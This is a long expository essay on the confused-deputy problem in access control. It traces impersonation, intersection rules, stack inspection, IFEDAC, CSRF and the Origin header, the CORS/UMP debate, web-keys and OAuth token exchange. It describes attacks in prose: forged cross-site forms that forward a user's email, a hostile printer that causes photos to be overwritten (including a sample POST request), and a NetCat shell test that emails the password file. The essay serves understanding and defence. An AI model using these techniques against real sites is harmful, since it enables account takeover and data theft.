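When a deputy runs under its caller's identity, the caller also can't limit what it does with each argument. *From ABAC to ZBAC* (Karp, Haury and Davis, 2009) gives the example of a user who copies one file to another and types the names in the wrong order. The user has permission to read and write both files, so the system lets the program overwrite the original. The user meant to grant read access to one file and write access to the other, but the system can't tell this from the user's identity. The paper proposes that the user attach a separate authorization to each argument, so that the swapped request fails.

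### Requests that pass through several services

A deputy often has to call another service, which must then decide whose permissions apply. Karp and colleagues argue that often neither the deputy's nor the caller's permissions are right. The deputy can be confused if it uses its own permissions, and if it uses the caller's, it can do anything at the second service that the caller could.

At its delegation level, Windows lets a server call other servers as its client. Microsoft's *Client Impersonation* describes a client that calls server A, which then calls server B as the client, and B cannot tell A's requests from the client's own. Microsoft calls delegation potentially dangerous because of the power it gives A. Kerberos, the only Microsoft security provider that supports delegation, requires the client and server to prove their identities to each other first, and administrators can restrict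 which computers may receive delegation-level calls. These measures help keep the client's identity away from untrustworthy servers, but they do not limit what a trusted server can do with it.

Karp and colleagues examined a US Navy trial in which a user called one service, which called a second one to get data. The second service received information about both the user and the first service. The implementers had two ways to avoid confused deputies and misuse of the user's identity. They could assume that the user fully trusted the first service, but then the user also had to trust the second service and any others further down the chain. Or they could have the second service accept only requests that the user had signed, but then the first service could only pass messages along. Karp and colleagues thought both options were awkward for work with coalition partners.

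Longer chains of calls need more identities than those of one caller and one deputy. In another of their examples, Alice asks Bob's backup service to save some data, and Bob's service uses Carol's copying service to do it. Alice may read the data, Bob may write to the storage, and Carol's service needs both permissions to make the copy. If it runs as Carol, the copy normally fails because she has neither permission. But if Carol has permission to use something that Alice can't, Alice can name it and get Carol's service to copy it for her. If Carol's service receives the identities of everyone earlier in the chain, it can use any of Alice's and Bob's permissions, even though the job involves only one input and one output.

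Systems made up of many small services commonly offer no way to delegate except impersonation, a limitation Karp criticised in Miller's 2026 thread. A developer building one has to choose between a service that attackers can confuse and a service that can do everything its users can. *Delegated Authority Problem Space Report*, a draft by Bucci, Caballero and colleagues that Karp edits, distinguishes impersonation from delegation using the example of a night club that admits anyone who knows a member's secret code. A member who tells a friend the code cannot later exclude the friend without changing the code for both of them, and the club cannot tell which of them came in. Delegation, in the draft's terms, gives the friend a permission that the member can cancel separately and that identifies who used it. By that standard, the level that Windows calls delegation is impersonation across machines.

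Karp's objection that a deputy may not be allowed to know its caller's permissions applies most directly to `access()` and the identification level, where the deputy looks up the caller's permissions or privileges. A deputy that impersonates Alice to open one file learns only whether that attempt succeeded. But it could try any other file the same way, so impersonation keeps her permissions private only if the deputy doesn't test them.

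Impersonation also gives no protection when someone other than the caller chose the file. Suppose Bob sends Alice source code containing an instruction to include the text of her private notes. She compiles it and returns the output to him. The compiler switches to Alice's identity before it opens the notes, and the kernel correctly finds that she may read them. Bob chose the file and could not have read it himself, but the kernel never checks his identity, because he did not call the compiler.

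## Checking everyone who influenced the request

When Bob hides an instruction in the source code that Alice compiles, the kernel checks whether Alice may read her notes and ignores Bob. Several groups of researchers have proposed keeping access lists but giving the check more than one identity. The usual rule is that a request may do only what everyone involved in it may do:

`rights(request) = rights(p1) ∩ rights(p2) ∩ ... ∩ rights(pn)`

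Here p1 to pn are the principals involved, and the symbol ∩ (intersection) keeps only the permissions that all of them have.

Suppose Alice runs the compiler and names BILL as her debugging file. The compiler may write to BILL but Alice may not, so the intersection of their permissions does not include writing to BILL, and the system refuses. The attack fails even if the compiler's programmer never considered it. But when the compiler tries to record Alice's charge, the principals, operation and file are the same, so the system refuses again and Tymshare cannot bill anyone. As expected from the two-case proof, adding the caller's name changes the decision but does not distinguish the attack from legitimate billing.

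The rule can also block a request because the deputy lacks a permission. If Alice's source code is private and the compiler is not on its access list, the compiler cannot read the program it is supposed to compile. Systems that use the rule usually give trusted code every permission or leave its permissions out of the intersection.

### Who counts as involved

Java and Microsoft's .NET platform run code from different sources inside one process, so their principals are mostly sources of code rather than users. They use stack inspection, which *Stack Inspection* (Fournet and Gordon, 2002) describes in detail. The call stack records the functions that have started but not yet finished. When the platform loads a function, it assigns the function permissions based on its source. Before trusted code uses a protected resource, a test checks the stack and fails unless every function on it has the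 required permission. If an applet that is not allowed to read files calls a library function that displays them, the test finds the applet on the stack and stops the read.

Critics complained that stack inspection depended on how Java happened to be implemented. Wallach and Felten answered in *Understanding Java Stack Inspection* that each decision corresponds to building a proof in an established logic of access control.

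The test protects trusted code from its callers but not from the code it calls, because a function leaves the stack when it finishes and the test then has no record of it. In one of Fournet and Gordon's examples, a trusted function calls an untrusted one to get a file name and then displays that file. The untrusted function returns "secrets" and leaves the stack before the test runs, so the test passes.

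Abadi and Fournet, in *Access Control based on Execution History*, base a program's rights on all the code that has run, including code that has already returned. The platform keeps the current rights in a variable and, whenever a piece of code runs, intersects them with that code's own rights. The reduced rights remain in force after the code returns. In their example, a program asks a plug-in for the name of a temporary file to delete, and the plug-in returns the path of a password file. Stack inspection allows the deletion because the plug-in is no longer on the stack, but history-based control refuses it because the program lost the right to delete files when the plug-in ran.

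Abadi and Fournet call their method an approximation because it tracks which code ran but not which data affected what. A program therefore loses its rights after running a harmless plug-in, even if it ignores the plug-in's answer. But the compiler keeps its rights when it reads Bob's source code, because it never runs that code.

Operating systems can keep a similar record in the names of their principals. *Access Control in a World of Software Diversity* (Abadi, Birrell and Wobber, 2005) proposed compound principals, which list the chain of programs behind a request. If Andrew logs in, starts a command shell and uses the program `cat` to open a file, the request comes from a principal with a name like `login@andrew + shell + cat`. The plus sign joins a program to the one that started it, and the @ sign marks a role a program has adopted, here that of the user whose password `login` accepted.

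In this design, an ACL is a pattern that the whole name must match, and the check doesn't intersect anything. For example, a file's owner could admit Ted only while he uses Microsoft Word, or admit Microsoft Office programs regardless of who runs them.

Wobber, Yumerefendi and colleagues built a version of this for Singularity, an experimental Microsoft operating system (*Authorizing Applications in Singularity*, 2007). They left out impersonation because they regarded it as a source of security holes. When a client lets an encryption service open files for it, the file server receives the name `client + service` instead of the client's name alone. They considered adding more to the names, such as each program's parameters and open files, but thought useful policies would soon become too difficult to write. The name covers only the programs that led to the current one, so if the compiler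 starts a helper that returns a file name, the helper does not appear in the compiler's name.

Mao, Li and colleagues (2009), in *Trojan Horse Resistant Discretionary Access Control*, track data as well as programs. They blame the weakness of ordinary access lists on the assumption that one principal is responsible for each request, when several may have influenced it. Their Linux system, IFEDAC, keeps a set of possible influences for every process and file. The set can contain ordinary users and `net`, which stands for anyone on the network. It changes as follows:

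- A new process inherits the set of the process that started it.
- A process that receives network traffic gains `net`.
- A process that reads or runs a file gains everything in the file's set.
- A file gains everything in the set of any process that writes to it.

The system allows an access only if the file's permissions allow it for every member of the process's set. These permissions normally come from the existing Linux settings, so users keep their current access lists.

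This stops Bob's attack. If Bob has an account on Alice's machine, his source file has the set {Bob}. The compiler starts with {Alice} and has {Alice, Bob} after reading the file. Bob may not read Alice's notes, so the system refuses to let the compiler open them. It also refuses to let the compiler save the compiled program in Alice's private directory, because Bob may not write there.

### Letting the compiler bill

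A deputy under the intersection rule needs some way to use a permission that its caller lacks. Stack inspection provides one with an operation that Fournet and Gordon call `grant`. In their example, a trusted function draws on the screen and also has to write to a performance log. When an applet calls the function, the write fails because the applet isn't allowed to use files. The function can use `grant` to make the platform ignore its callers when checking that permission.

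In their notation, S is the set of permissions that a piece of code has because of its source, and D is the set available to it at the moment. The expression `grant R in e` runs e with D ∪ (R ∩ S), which adds the permissions in R that the code already had in S. A function can therefore recover its own permissions but cannot give itself new ones. Applied to the compiler, with Alice as its caller, this works as follows:

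1. D starts as the permissions that Alice and the compiler share, which include writing Alice's files but not BILL.
2. The debugging code tries to write to BILL, and the check refuses.
3. The billing code runs `grant {write BILL}` around the charge, and the check allows it.
4. When the charge is complete, D returns to its earlier value.

Both answers are now right, but only because the programmer put `grant` around one write and not the other. If both jobs call a shared function that opens whatever file it receives, and the programmer puts `grant` inside that function, Alice can overwrite BILL again. Fournet and Gordon give the example of a function that lets any caller read the operating system's version. It can safely override the check because it supplies the file name itself. Using `grant` this way is an endorsement, an explicit decision by the deputy to let an outsider's input affect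 a protected resource.

Abadi and Fournet keep `grant` and add `accept`, which lets a program recover rights it lost by running less trusted code, such as a plug-in. The program saves its rights, runs the plug-in, checks the result and then calls `accept`. The programmer thereby takes responsibility for whatever the plug-in did. They regard this as a benefit, because auditors know where to look and whom to blame. An administrator can also make some rights unrecoverable. In their example, a customer's program may use code from either of two competing contractors, but once it has used one, it can no longer use the other. Unrecoverable rights would not suit the compiler, which must be able to bill after every job.

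Compound principals make the charge easy to allow. BILL's list can admit the compiler no matter who started it, as Wobber and colleagues suggest for a computer game that records high scores. But the debugging code has the same compound name as the billing code, so BILL's list admits it too. Wobber and colleagues concede that such a list doesn't stop an attacker from misusing the program, although it limits the attacker to what the program can do.

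Roles can separate the compiler's two jobs. In the 2005 design, a program can start a copy of itself under a role, so the compiler could record charges as `compiler@billing`, and BILL's access list could admit only that role. This is safe as long as the copy never opens a file that Alice named, which again depends on the programmer. An administrator can also mark a program as a service, whose name leaves out whoever started it. A compiler running as a service would have the same problem as Hardy's, because its requests would carry only its own identity.

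IFEDAC handles such cases with exceptions for particular programs. When Alice changes her password, the `passwd` program runs with the set {Alice}, but an exception lets it write to `/etc/shadow`, the protected password file. The same kind of exception would let the compiler write to BILL, but it would apply to the whole program, so the debugging code could also write there and the original attack would work.

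The policy's author could instead give the exception to a small billing program, since a process loses its exceptions when it loads another program. But Alice could then run that program herself and add false charges, as with the separate logging program on Unix. Mao and colleagues explicitly assume that programs with exceptions either handle their input correctly or fail in ways that an attacker cannot directly exploit. IFEDAC tracks more than the other designs, but its override is less precise than `grant`, which can cover a single operation.

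The intersection rule still has an advantage over impersonation because it makes programmers' mistakes easier to notice. Forgetting to switch identities may go unnoticed, but forgetting a `grant` makes billing fail the first time anyone uses the compiler.

Failures also give programmers a reason to override the check too freely. Fournet and Gordon note that an unexpected refusal is a more immediate worry for a programmer than a possible attack. Abadi and Fournet report that programmers concerned about speed often replace stack inspection with faster but riskier checks.

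### The Linux prototype

Mao and colleagues tested IFEDAC on a Linux server and a personal workstation. To imitate a server that an attacker had taken over, they ran the network tool NetCat as the administrator and set it to give a command shell to anyone who connected. From that shell they tried to install two rootkits (software that hides an intruder's control of a machine), email the password file to themselves and change another user's web page. All of these attacks succeeded on ordinary Linux but failed with IFEDAC, where the shell had the set {`net`}.

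They also ran Agobot, a program that takes commands from a remote attacker, as though the administrator had opened it from an email. IFEDAC kept it from changing protected files or adding itself to the programs that start with the machine, but it did not stop the bot from sending spam, scanning other computers or joining attacks that flood a website with traffic, because these actions don't require access to protected files.

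These results are good evidence that tracking influence confines programs that an attacker controls. They are weaker evidence about confused deputies, because neither NetCat nor the bot had an exception for the files under attack. A closer test would have been to trick `passwd` or another program into misusing its own exception.

Most programs ran without changes. The sample policy lists exceptions for seven network programs and twenty programs that run with the administrator's user ID, such as `passwd`. Some programs also need exemptions from the tracking itself. Without one, the remote login server would gain `net` as soon as anyone connected, and nobody could use it to administer the machine. The software that draws the desktop also needs one because it takes input from every application on the screen.

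The email program Thunderbird, for example, gains `net` when it fetches mail, and then needs an exception to write to its own message folder. The user saves attachments in a special directory that admits `net`, and must upgrade a file by hand before treating it as trustworthy, so users have to make endorsements too.

IFEDAC slowed operations by 3% to 19% in one set of benchmarks and by 4% to 26% in another. Mao and colleagues considered this slowdown comparable to SELinux's, an established security system for Linux.

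Abadi and Fournet had a smaller compatibility problem, because history-based access control never grants more rights than stack inspection. Existing programs would be at least as secure as before but might run into new refusals. They expected few refusals, since trusted libraries rarely depended on less trusted code, but they had not built the method into .NET to check this.

### Close's objection to stack inspection

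In *ACLs don't*, Close argues that access decisions "cannot be correctly done using stack introspection" because it tracks too little.

Stack inspection doesn't account for functions that have returned, and it covers only one process. Abadi and Fournet explain that the .NET platform does its own checks and then calls the operating system with all its privileges. The kernel therefore receives only the platform's identity, however carefully the platform inspected the stack.

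The other designs record more, so Close's objection applies to them less or not at all. Suppose Alice is using the compiler honestly and an outsider wants the compiler to open her private notes. The outsider can supply the file's name in several ways. The table assumes that neither the outsider nor the plug-in has permission to read the notes, and that no override covers the notes.

| What the system records | A downloaded plug-in runs the compiler and gives it the name | The compiler runs the plug-in, which returns the name | The name is in source code that Bob wrote |
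|---|---|---|---|
| Functions on the call stack | Refuses | Allows | Allows |
| All code that has run | Refuses | Refuses | Allows |
| The chain of programs | Refuses if the notes' list admits only trusted programs | Allows | Allows |
| The origins of data | Refuses | Refuses | Refuses |

Close is right about the first row, but the last row shows that his objection doesn't apply to every system that uses access lists. IFEDAC keeps the information when data passes through files or between processes on the same machine, and it still checks access by looking up identities in a list.

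A set of influences still does not show which principal goes with which file. Alice and Bob may each read only their own sales file, and both want the program to read and combine the two. Once the program's set is {Alice, Bob}, the intersection rule stops it from reading either file. The program would need an override for each file, and its programmer would have to match each override to the right person.

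None of these designs can approve the compiler's charge automatically, because of the same gap. Alice started the compiler and it has read her input, so she has influenced the whole process, including the billing code. Labelling each value separately, as provenance tracking does, would allow the check to distinguish the two writes, so Hardy's exercise does not rule out every identity-based check.

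Even then, the charge would depend on what Alice asked the compiler to do, and somebody would have to decide that this dependence was acceptable. With capabilities, the programmer also makes that decision, but the system doesn't have to track who influenced the request.

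## Checking which website a request came from

IFEDAC can follow influence from one file to another because a single operating system handles every read and write. A web server receives a request from a user's browser, usually with a cookie that identifies the user, but it can't see which page made the browser send the request. The browser has that information and can send it to the server.

Suppose Alice has logged in to her email site, which has a form for forwarding her mail to another address. Close's *Web-key* describes how another site can use that form. The attacker's page contains a copy of it, with the attacker's address filled in and a script that submits it when the page loads. Alice's browser sends the request to the email site with her cookie attached. The email site receives the same URL, form contents and cookie as it would from its own page, so it starts forwarding her mail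 to the attacker.

This attack is called cross-site request forgery (CSRF), although Close points out that the request isn't forged, since it comes from Alice's browser. The browser is the deputy, and it combines the attacker's designation with the authority of Alice's cookie.

Gmail had a vulnerability of this kind in 2007. Barth, Jackson and Mitchell (2008), in *Robust Defenses for Cross-Site Request Forgery*, report that an attacker used it to forward David Airey's email and then took over his domain name, though Airey later repudiated the incident. They add that an attacker can use a browser inside a company to reach machines behind the firewall that the attacker cannot reach directly.

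The most popular defence at the time was a secret token. The site puts a random value in a hidden field of its own forms and rejects any submission without it, and the attacker's page can't read the site's forms to copy the value. Barth and colleagues found that many sites got this wrong. A tool called NoForge added the token to every link on a page, including links to other sites, which then received it. Sites also tended to leave their login forms unprotected, since there is no session to tie a token to until the user has logged in. An attacker could log Alice in to a search engine under the attacker's account and later read her searches in that account's history.

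### The Origin header

Browsers already sent a header, Referer, containing the address of the page that a request came from. A server could use it to refuse forged requests, but only if the header arrived reliably. In April 2008, Barth and colleagues tested this by buying 283,945 displays of an advertisement, across two advertising networks, that sent test requests to their own servers. The header was missing or wrong for roughly 3% to 11% of users over unencrypted connections, but for only 0.05% to 0.22% over HTTPS. Network proxies can strip headers from unencrypted traffic but not from HTTPS, so they concluded that proxies had removed most of the missing headers, probably for privacy, since a full address can reveal what someone searched for or how a company's internal site is organised.

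A site that accepted requests without the header gained no protection, because an attacker can make the browser omit it. Refusing such requests over unencrypted connections would have turned away many honest users.

They proposed a new header, Origin, which contains only the scheme, host and port of the page that started the request. The browser would send it with every POST request, the kind that submits a form, and would send the value `null` if it couldn't determine the origin. The server then follows two rules:

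1. Change stored data only in response to POST requests.
2. If the Origin header is present, refuse any value that is not on the site's own list, including `null`.

A browser that supports the Origin header always sends it with POST requests, so an attacker can't suppress the header to make a request look as if it came from an older browser. Barth and colleagues implemented the server's part in three lines of firewall rules and the browser's part in an eight-line patch to WebKit, Safari's engine.

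The check now also takes the request's origin as an input, so it becomes f(user, origin, operation, resource). Alice's own change to her forwarding address arrives as (Alice, email site, change, forwarding), and the forged one as (Alice, attacker's site, change, forwarding). An ordinary lookup can allow the first and refuse the second, which it could not do when it relied on the cookie alone.

The first rule covers a case that checking the origin misses. Many forums let people post images by giving an address, and each reader's browser fetches the image with a GET request, the kind that loads a page or picture. An attacker can post an address of their choosing, and the request will have the correct origin because it starts from the forum's own page. Barth and colleagues therefore have the server refuse to change anything in response to a GET request.

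### The photo printer

By default a page can send requests to other sites but can't read the replies. Cross-origin resource sharing (CORS) lets a server make exceptions. The browser sends the page's origin with the request, the server's reply includes a header stating which origins may read it, and the browser gives the reply to the page only if the page's origin is allowed. For methods other than GET and POST, the browser first sends a "preflight" request to find out whether the server accepts them. The page can also have the browser attach the user's cookies.

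CORS lets sites work together inside the user's browser, so one job can involve more than two parties. In June 2009, while engineers at the World Wide Web Consortium (W3C) were still designing CORS, Close took them through his printing example message by message. The example involves a photo manager, a photo printer and the storage service they share. The user wants to print `photo123`.

1. A page from the photo site asks the printer for a new print job. The request carries the photo site's origin.
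2. The printer creates an empty file, `job123`, at the storage service, gives the photo site permission to write to it, and replies with its address.
3. The photo page asks the storage service to copy `photo123` to `job123`. The storage service sees the photo site's origin, finds that this origin may read the first file and write to the second, and makes the copy.

Now suppose the printer is hostile. At step 2 it replies with the address of `photo456`, another of the user's pictures. The photo page carries on as before:

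```
POST /copydocument
Origin: photo.example.com

from: photo123
to:   photo456
```

The storage service correctly identifies the photo site as the origin, and the photo site is allowed to write to its own pictures, so the service overwrites `photo456`. The printer could not have done this itself, but it named the file and the photo site supplied the authority. Close concluded that a site cannot safely send an identifier it got from a third party to a server that decides access by origin.

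### The same job with web-keys

Close's alternative is the web-key, an HTTPS address that contains a long random string and grants permission to use one resource in one way. The server lets anyone who has the address use it, without checking who they are. Close suggests 64 random bits, which take 13 characters to write. If a server has issued a million web-keys and can answer a thousand requests a second, an attacker needs about 18 trillion guesses (2⁶⁴ ÷ 10⁶) on average to find a valid one. Close estimates that an attacker would need 292 years for an even chance of finding one, if the server did nothing but answer guesses.

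The string goes after a `#` sign because browsers leave that part of an address out of the Referer header, so other sites don't receive it. A script on the page extracts the string and sends it to the server in a separate request.

Close (2009) left the web-key version of the printing job as an exercise for the reader, but wrote it out the next year in *Implementor interest in a W3C WebApps proposal*, a thread on a Chromium developers' mailing list (Barth, 2010). The three steps are the same, but every file has an unguessable address and no request includes cookies or an origin. The printer creates a job file and replies with its web-key. The photo page sends the storage service that web-key and the one for `photo123`, and the service makes the copy. A hostile printer can't reply with the web-key for `photo456` because it doesn't have it. It could reply with the web-key of another file that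 it may write to, but that wouldn't let it do anything it couldn't do directly.

Dirk Pranke, a Chromium developer, thought this showed that the flaw in the original was guessable file names, not the Origin header. The attack does require the printer to know the name `photo456`. But ordinary names aren't meant to be secret, and a user who shows the printer a picture reveals its address. With web-keys, the user can give the printer an address that only permits reading, so the printer can't overwrite the file.

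Secret addresses can leak because they end up in bookmarks, server logs and browser histories, and on screens that other people can see. The standards for web addresses therefore advise against putting passwords in them. Close answers that a leaked web-key gives away one permission, not a whole account, and that administrators can protect logs and bookmarks. That reduces the damage from a leak, but administrators and users still have secrets to protect.

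Close and Miller turned the idea into a proposed standard, the Uniform Messaging Policy (UMP). Under UMP, a cross-site request carries no cookies, login details or origin, so any permission it needs must be in its address or contents. Rees identified one kind of forgery that UMP doesn't prevent, which targets machines that rely on a firewall or the caller's network address and mistakenly opt in to cross-site requests.

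### Checking the printer's answer

Ian Hickson, who edited the HTML standard, replied that the photo site in the example was at fault for trusting potentially hostile input (Hickson 2009, *XHR and sandboxed iframes*). He didn't see why the site would accept an address from the printer when that address might point to one of the site's own files. Close asked what validation the site should have done.

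Pranke later answered that the photo site could require the printer's address to begin with `job` and not `photo`, which he said developers do all the time in specific applications. This works in the example, and is similar to having a compiler screen file names before opening them. But the photo site has to know how the storage service arranges its addresses. Close pointed to the Atom Publishing Protocol, a standard for creating and editing entries on sites such as blogs, which leaves the form of addresses entirely to the server. A program that works with any Atom server therefore has no pattern to check against.

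Aaron Boodman, also in the Chromium thread, gave a concrete example of this. A company's internal news page publishes its stories through Blogger, which replies to each new story with the address to use for later edits. If Blogger turned hostile, it could reply with the address of the company's page for changing where salaries go. The news page would send its next edit there, from behind the firewall.

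Boodman doubted that this was realistic, because the attacker would have to control the whole request and not just its address. He also thought the salary page should have its own origin. Close replied that a separate origin for salaries would not help if Blogger instead returned an address belonging to the news page's own data. Boodman's doubt about controlling the whole request is reasonable for a salary form, which expects particular fields. It is weaker for the photo printer, because the request is already a command to overwrite a file and the attacker only has to change which file.

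### "Don't Be a Deputy"

In October 2009, Maciej Stachowiak of Apple offered the most detailed defence, proposing two changes to the storage service (Stachowiak 2009). The first is a one-time write token. The printer gets a token for its own job file and passes it to the photo site, which presents it when it makes the copy. The printer can't get a token for `photo456`, so the attack fails as long as the storage service requires a valid token. If the service falls back on the photo site's origin when a token is missing or invalid, either source of authority is enough again, as in Hardy's operating system.

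The second is a "conditional write", which copies a file only if the requesting origin and every other party listed in the request have permission to write to the destination. The photo site lists the printer, which has no permission to write to `photo456`, so the copy fails. This applies the intersection rule to a single file, so it allows the honest job, where both sites may write to `job123`. But if the photo site's programmer forgets to list the printer, honest jobs still work and nobody notices the vulnerability.

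An hour later Stachowiak added that the photo site could send the printer the picture itself, so no third party's address would be involved. He called Close's scenario somewhat contrived because it didn't do this. He also suggested giving the printer permission to read the picture where it was. Close answered that a hostile photo site could then send the address of the printer's own client list and receive a printout of it. Stachowiak replied that if the user may not see the list, a request with the user's cookie shouldn't be able to fetch it. That defence works only if the storage service checks the user as well as the printer's origin.

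In November, after a W3C meeting, Stachowiak generalised his answer into a rule called "Don't Be a Deputy" (quoted in Sicking, 2009). Under this rule, a site must either never make a request to one site on behalf of another, or make sure that every request it makes for a third party looks different from any request it makes for itself.

Stachowiak then redesigned the storage service to follow the second option. Each file belongs to one site, and an ordinary copy command works only within the requesting site's own files. Copying between sites needs a different command, which takes both owners' names, a one-time read token for the source and a one-time write token for the destination. Only a file's owner can get tokens for it. If the printer now replies with `photo456`, the photo site sends the cross-site command and names the printer as the destination's owner. The service refuses because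 `photo456` doesn't belong to the printer and the command has no valid write token for it.

If a programmer used the ordinary copy command by mistake, every legitimate print job would fail, because `job123` belongs to the printer. So this design, unlike the conditional write, exposes the mistake early. But the tokens provide most of the protection. Stachowiak acknowledged that the origin and cookie were arguably unnecessary for the cross-site copy, though he thought they made the system easier to build and more robust.

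Close criticized the rule in the Chromium thread. He read its first option as a ban on cross-site messaging, since some of the data in a cross-site request, such as its address, always comes from the other site. He said he didn't understand how the second option worked, although Stachowiak's storage commands are an example of it. His better argument, made in April 2010, was that nobody had explained the rule to developers. He expected them to find it onerous and error-prone if anyone did.

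Jonas Sicking, another member of the group, suggested making the second option easy by giving pages a separate kind of request that never includes any identity. A site would use it whenever it acted for somebody else. This is nearly the same as UMP, offered alongside CORS rather than in place of it.

By then the disagreement was mostly about defaults. In December 2009 Stachowiak described two schools of thought. One wanted to encourage capabilities by refusing to extend the use of origins and cookies. The other thought the web was probably stuck with the existing model, and wanted to build on it and find practical ways to reduce its risks. Like Barth, Stachowiak did not expect more debate to settle the disagreement.

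Hickson (2010) argued that developers could misuse either system, and that CORS was vulnerable only when sites shared identifiers without validating them. Sicking gave the example of a developer using UMP who might write one function that fetches any address it receives and adds the same security token each time. Close (2010) paraphrased this as saying that because developers might build something broken, browsers should give them something already broken. Sicking's example is still a real hazard, because a token added to every request is ambient authority, whether the browser or the programmer adds it. UMP makes per-resource permissions possible but can't force anyone to use them.

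### Whether CORS created a new danger

Miller (2009) argued that CORS only postponed request forgery by one level and created "second order" confused deputies. In ordinary forgery the attacker's page misleads the browser, whereas in the printing example the browser reports the origin correctly but the printer misleads the photo site. When others dismissed the example, Miller replied that request forgery must have seemed theoretical when someone first diagnosed it. In the Chromium thread he estimated that about five years passed between browsers introducing that weakness and the first report of someone exploiting it.

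In December 2011, Brad Hill, co-chair of the W3C group that later took over CORS, reviewed the archived debate. He concluded that CORS gave request forgers no qualitatively new ability, since forms had allowed cross-site POST requests almost from the beginning of the web (Hill, 2011). He had asked Miller and Close to bring any remaining issues to the group but had received no reply. He agreed that automatic credentials raised a real question, but thought it extended beyond CORS and was no reason to delay it.

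Hill is right about a forger who only sends requests. Close's example is different because the photo page has to read the printer's reply, which a form submission doesn't allow. Close had made this point in 2010, and Pranke agreed there was a difference. But Boodman and Adam Barth listed older ways for a site to receive an address from another site: communication between servers, browser plug-ins, and a trick with hidden frames that Facebook's login service used on many sites. A developer could therefore have built the vulnerable photo site before CORS existed. CORS made it easier to build, in code that runs with the user's cookies and behind the user's firewall.

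Nobody could say how much that mattered. In 2010, Pranke knew of no attacks through CORS, but he also knew of nobody using it. Stachowiak thought sites that worked together almost always did so in pairs, while Close expected requests combining data from several sites to be common in cross-site applications, but neither had measurements.

### What browsers adopted

By April 2010, Safari, Chrome and Firefox had shipped CORS, and Internet Explorer had a limited version. Barth wrote that browser makers didn't want to remove CORS. He recommended publishing UMP as a separate document for web developers and having browser makers work from one specification that covered both UMP and CORS.

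*We Still Don't Have Secure Cross-Domain Requests* (Chen, Jiang and colleagues) describes CORS as supported by all web browsers. By contrast, *Uniform Messaging Policy, Level One* (Close and Miller, 2014), the specification for UMP, was published as a W3C Note in October 2014 with a notice that work on it had stopped and that nobody should use it as a basis for implementation.

CORS keeps part of UMP's idea. In *CORS is Stupid*, Cox (2024) recommends that most sites answer cross-site requests with a wildcard, which allows every origin but only for requests without the user's credentials. He warns that listing particular origins may create a false sense of security. The browser still sends the origin with these requests, so a server can wrongly grant permissions based on it.

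Browsers also fixed a weakness that Close had found in redirects. In June 2009 Close described a page that sends a request to an attacker's server, which redirects the browser back to the page's own site. The site then received a request that carried its own origin and the user's cookies but went to a destination the attacker had chosen. The designers first planned to make the Origin header list every site in the redirect chain. Miller objected that this would treat only the symptom.

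Browsers eventually kept a single value in the `Origin` header because CORS compares it with an exact string. They changed that value to `null` once a redirect crosses from one origin to another. Hill (2015), in *Origin HTTP header not set to null after following cross-origin redirect*, reported that WebKit was still preserving the original value and warned that this could create a confused deputy. The change to `null` works because the browser performs the redirect and can record it. In the printing example, though, a script reads an address from one reply and puts it in a new request, which the browser treats as an ordinary request from the photo site.

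Two later mechanisms address ordinary forgery. A server can mark a cookie as SameSite so that the browser leaves it off form submissions from other sites. Cox recommends this as the default and notes that it blocks every cross-site form post, with no way to exempt a few addresses. Browsers also send a header called Sec-Fetch-Site, which classifies each request as coming from the same origin, the same site (a broader group that includes a domain's subdomains), another site, or the user directly, as with a bookmark. The server can refuse cross-site requests without keeping a list of origins, and browsers send the header with GET requests too.

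Neither helps the storage service. The photo site's request is cross-site whether or not the printer is honest, so refusing cross-site requests would break the printing service as well as stop the attack. If the storage service needs the user's cookie to make the copy, it has to allow that cookie on cross-site requests, and the hostile printer can use the same exception. The forum image also gets through, because its request comes from the forum's own page.

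Request forgery remains common even though the remedies take little work. MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses* (2025), an annual ranking by the non-profit organisation that catalogues types of software flaw, ranks it third. It was fourth in MITRE's *2024 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses* (2024) and ninth the year before that. MITRE (2025) counted 1,750 reported request forgery vulnerabilities, up from 1,301, although their share of the reports behind the list fell slightly, from 6.6% to 6.2%. None of them appears in the catalogue of vulnerabilities that attackers are known to have exploited. These figures suggest that many sites still omit a check, but they are not evidence that the check fails on sites that use it.

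The 2025 list also includes server-side request forgery, in 22nd place, which origin checks don't address. In this attack, an outsider gives a server an address to fetch, and the server fetches it using its own network access. There may be no browser to report an origin.

### Two parties and three

The Origin header identifies the site whose page sent a request. Checking it is enough when that site also chose everything in the request, as the email example shows. The table applies the check to four requests from this section.

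| Request | Who chose the address to change | Origin that the server receives | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| An attacker's page submits the email forwarding form | The attacker | The attacker's site | Refuses, correctly |
| An attacker's server redirects a page's request back to the page's own site | The attacker | `null` | Refuses, correctly |
| The photo site saves the user's edit to `photo456` | The photo site | The photo site | Allows, correctly |
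| The photo site copies a picture to `photo456` because the printer named it | The printer | The photo site | Allows, wrongly |

The last two rows are the compiler's two writes again, with the same inputs for both.

A longer Origin header would not separate them unless the photo site reported where it got the address. Close's last argument in the Chromium thread was that a request involving several parties has no single origin, since one party may have supplied one identifier, another party a second, and a third may have sent the request. In the printing job, `photo123` came from the photo site and `photo456` from the printer, so the storage service would need to know where each address came from.

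## Tying a credential to one user, one service and one purpose

The storage service could not detect that the printer had chosen `photo456`, because it received only the photo site's origin and perhaps the user's cookie. A credential made for one job can carry more information. Stachowiak's one-time write token was an early example, and several OAuth standards have since developed the idea. OAuth is a framework that lets users give an application access to their data without sharing their password. An authorization server (the issuer) gives the application a token, and the application presents it to the service that holds the data (the receiver).

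An ordinary token may identify only the user and a broad permission, such as reading email. The newer standards add fields for the acting service, the intended receiver, the exact operation and the transaction. Defenders of identity-based checks now answer Hardy's exercise with these narrower credentials, which still identify the user to the receiver but cover much less than everything that user may do.

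### What each field adds

Jones, Nadalin and colleagues, in *OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange*, define a way for a service to get a token that identifies its caller. The Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which sets many of the internet's technical standards, published it as RFC 8693. A typical exchange has four steps:

1. Alice's application calls a front-end service and presents her token.
2. The front end sends her token to the issuer, proves its own identity and names the back-end service it wants to call.
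3. The issuer checks the request and returns a new token for the back end. In one example, this token lasts for one minute.
4. The front end calls the back end with the new token.

Engineers often call the result an on-behalf-of token, which can take two forms. With impersonation, the token's subject is Alice and the back end cannot distinguish the front end from her. With delegation, the subject is still Alice, but a second field names the front end as the actor.

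If the compiler used delegation, it would record the charge with its own token and write the debugging output with a token for Alice that names the compiler as actor. The access check would then receive different inputs for the two writes, so BILL's access list could allow the first and refuse the second. As with impersonation on Windows, the programmer would have to use the right credential for each write. The actor field would also let a file's owner give Alice fewer rights when she acts through the compiler than when she acts directly.

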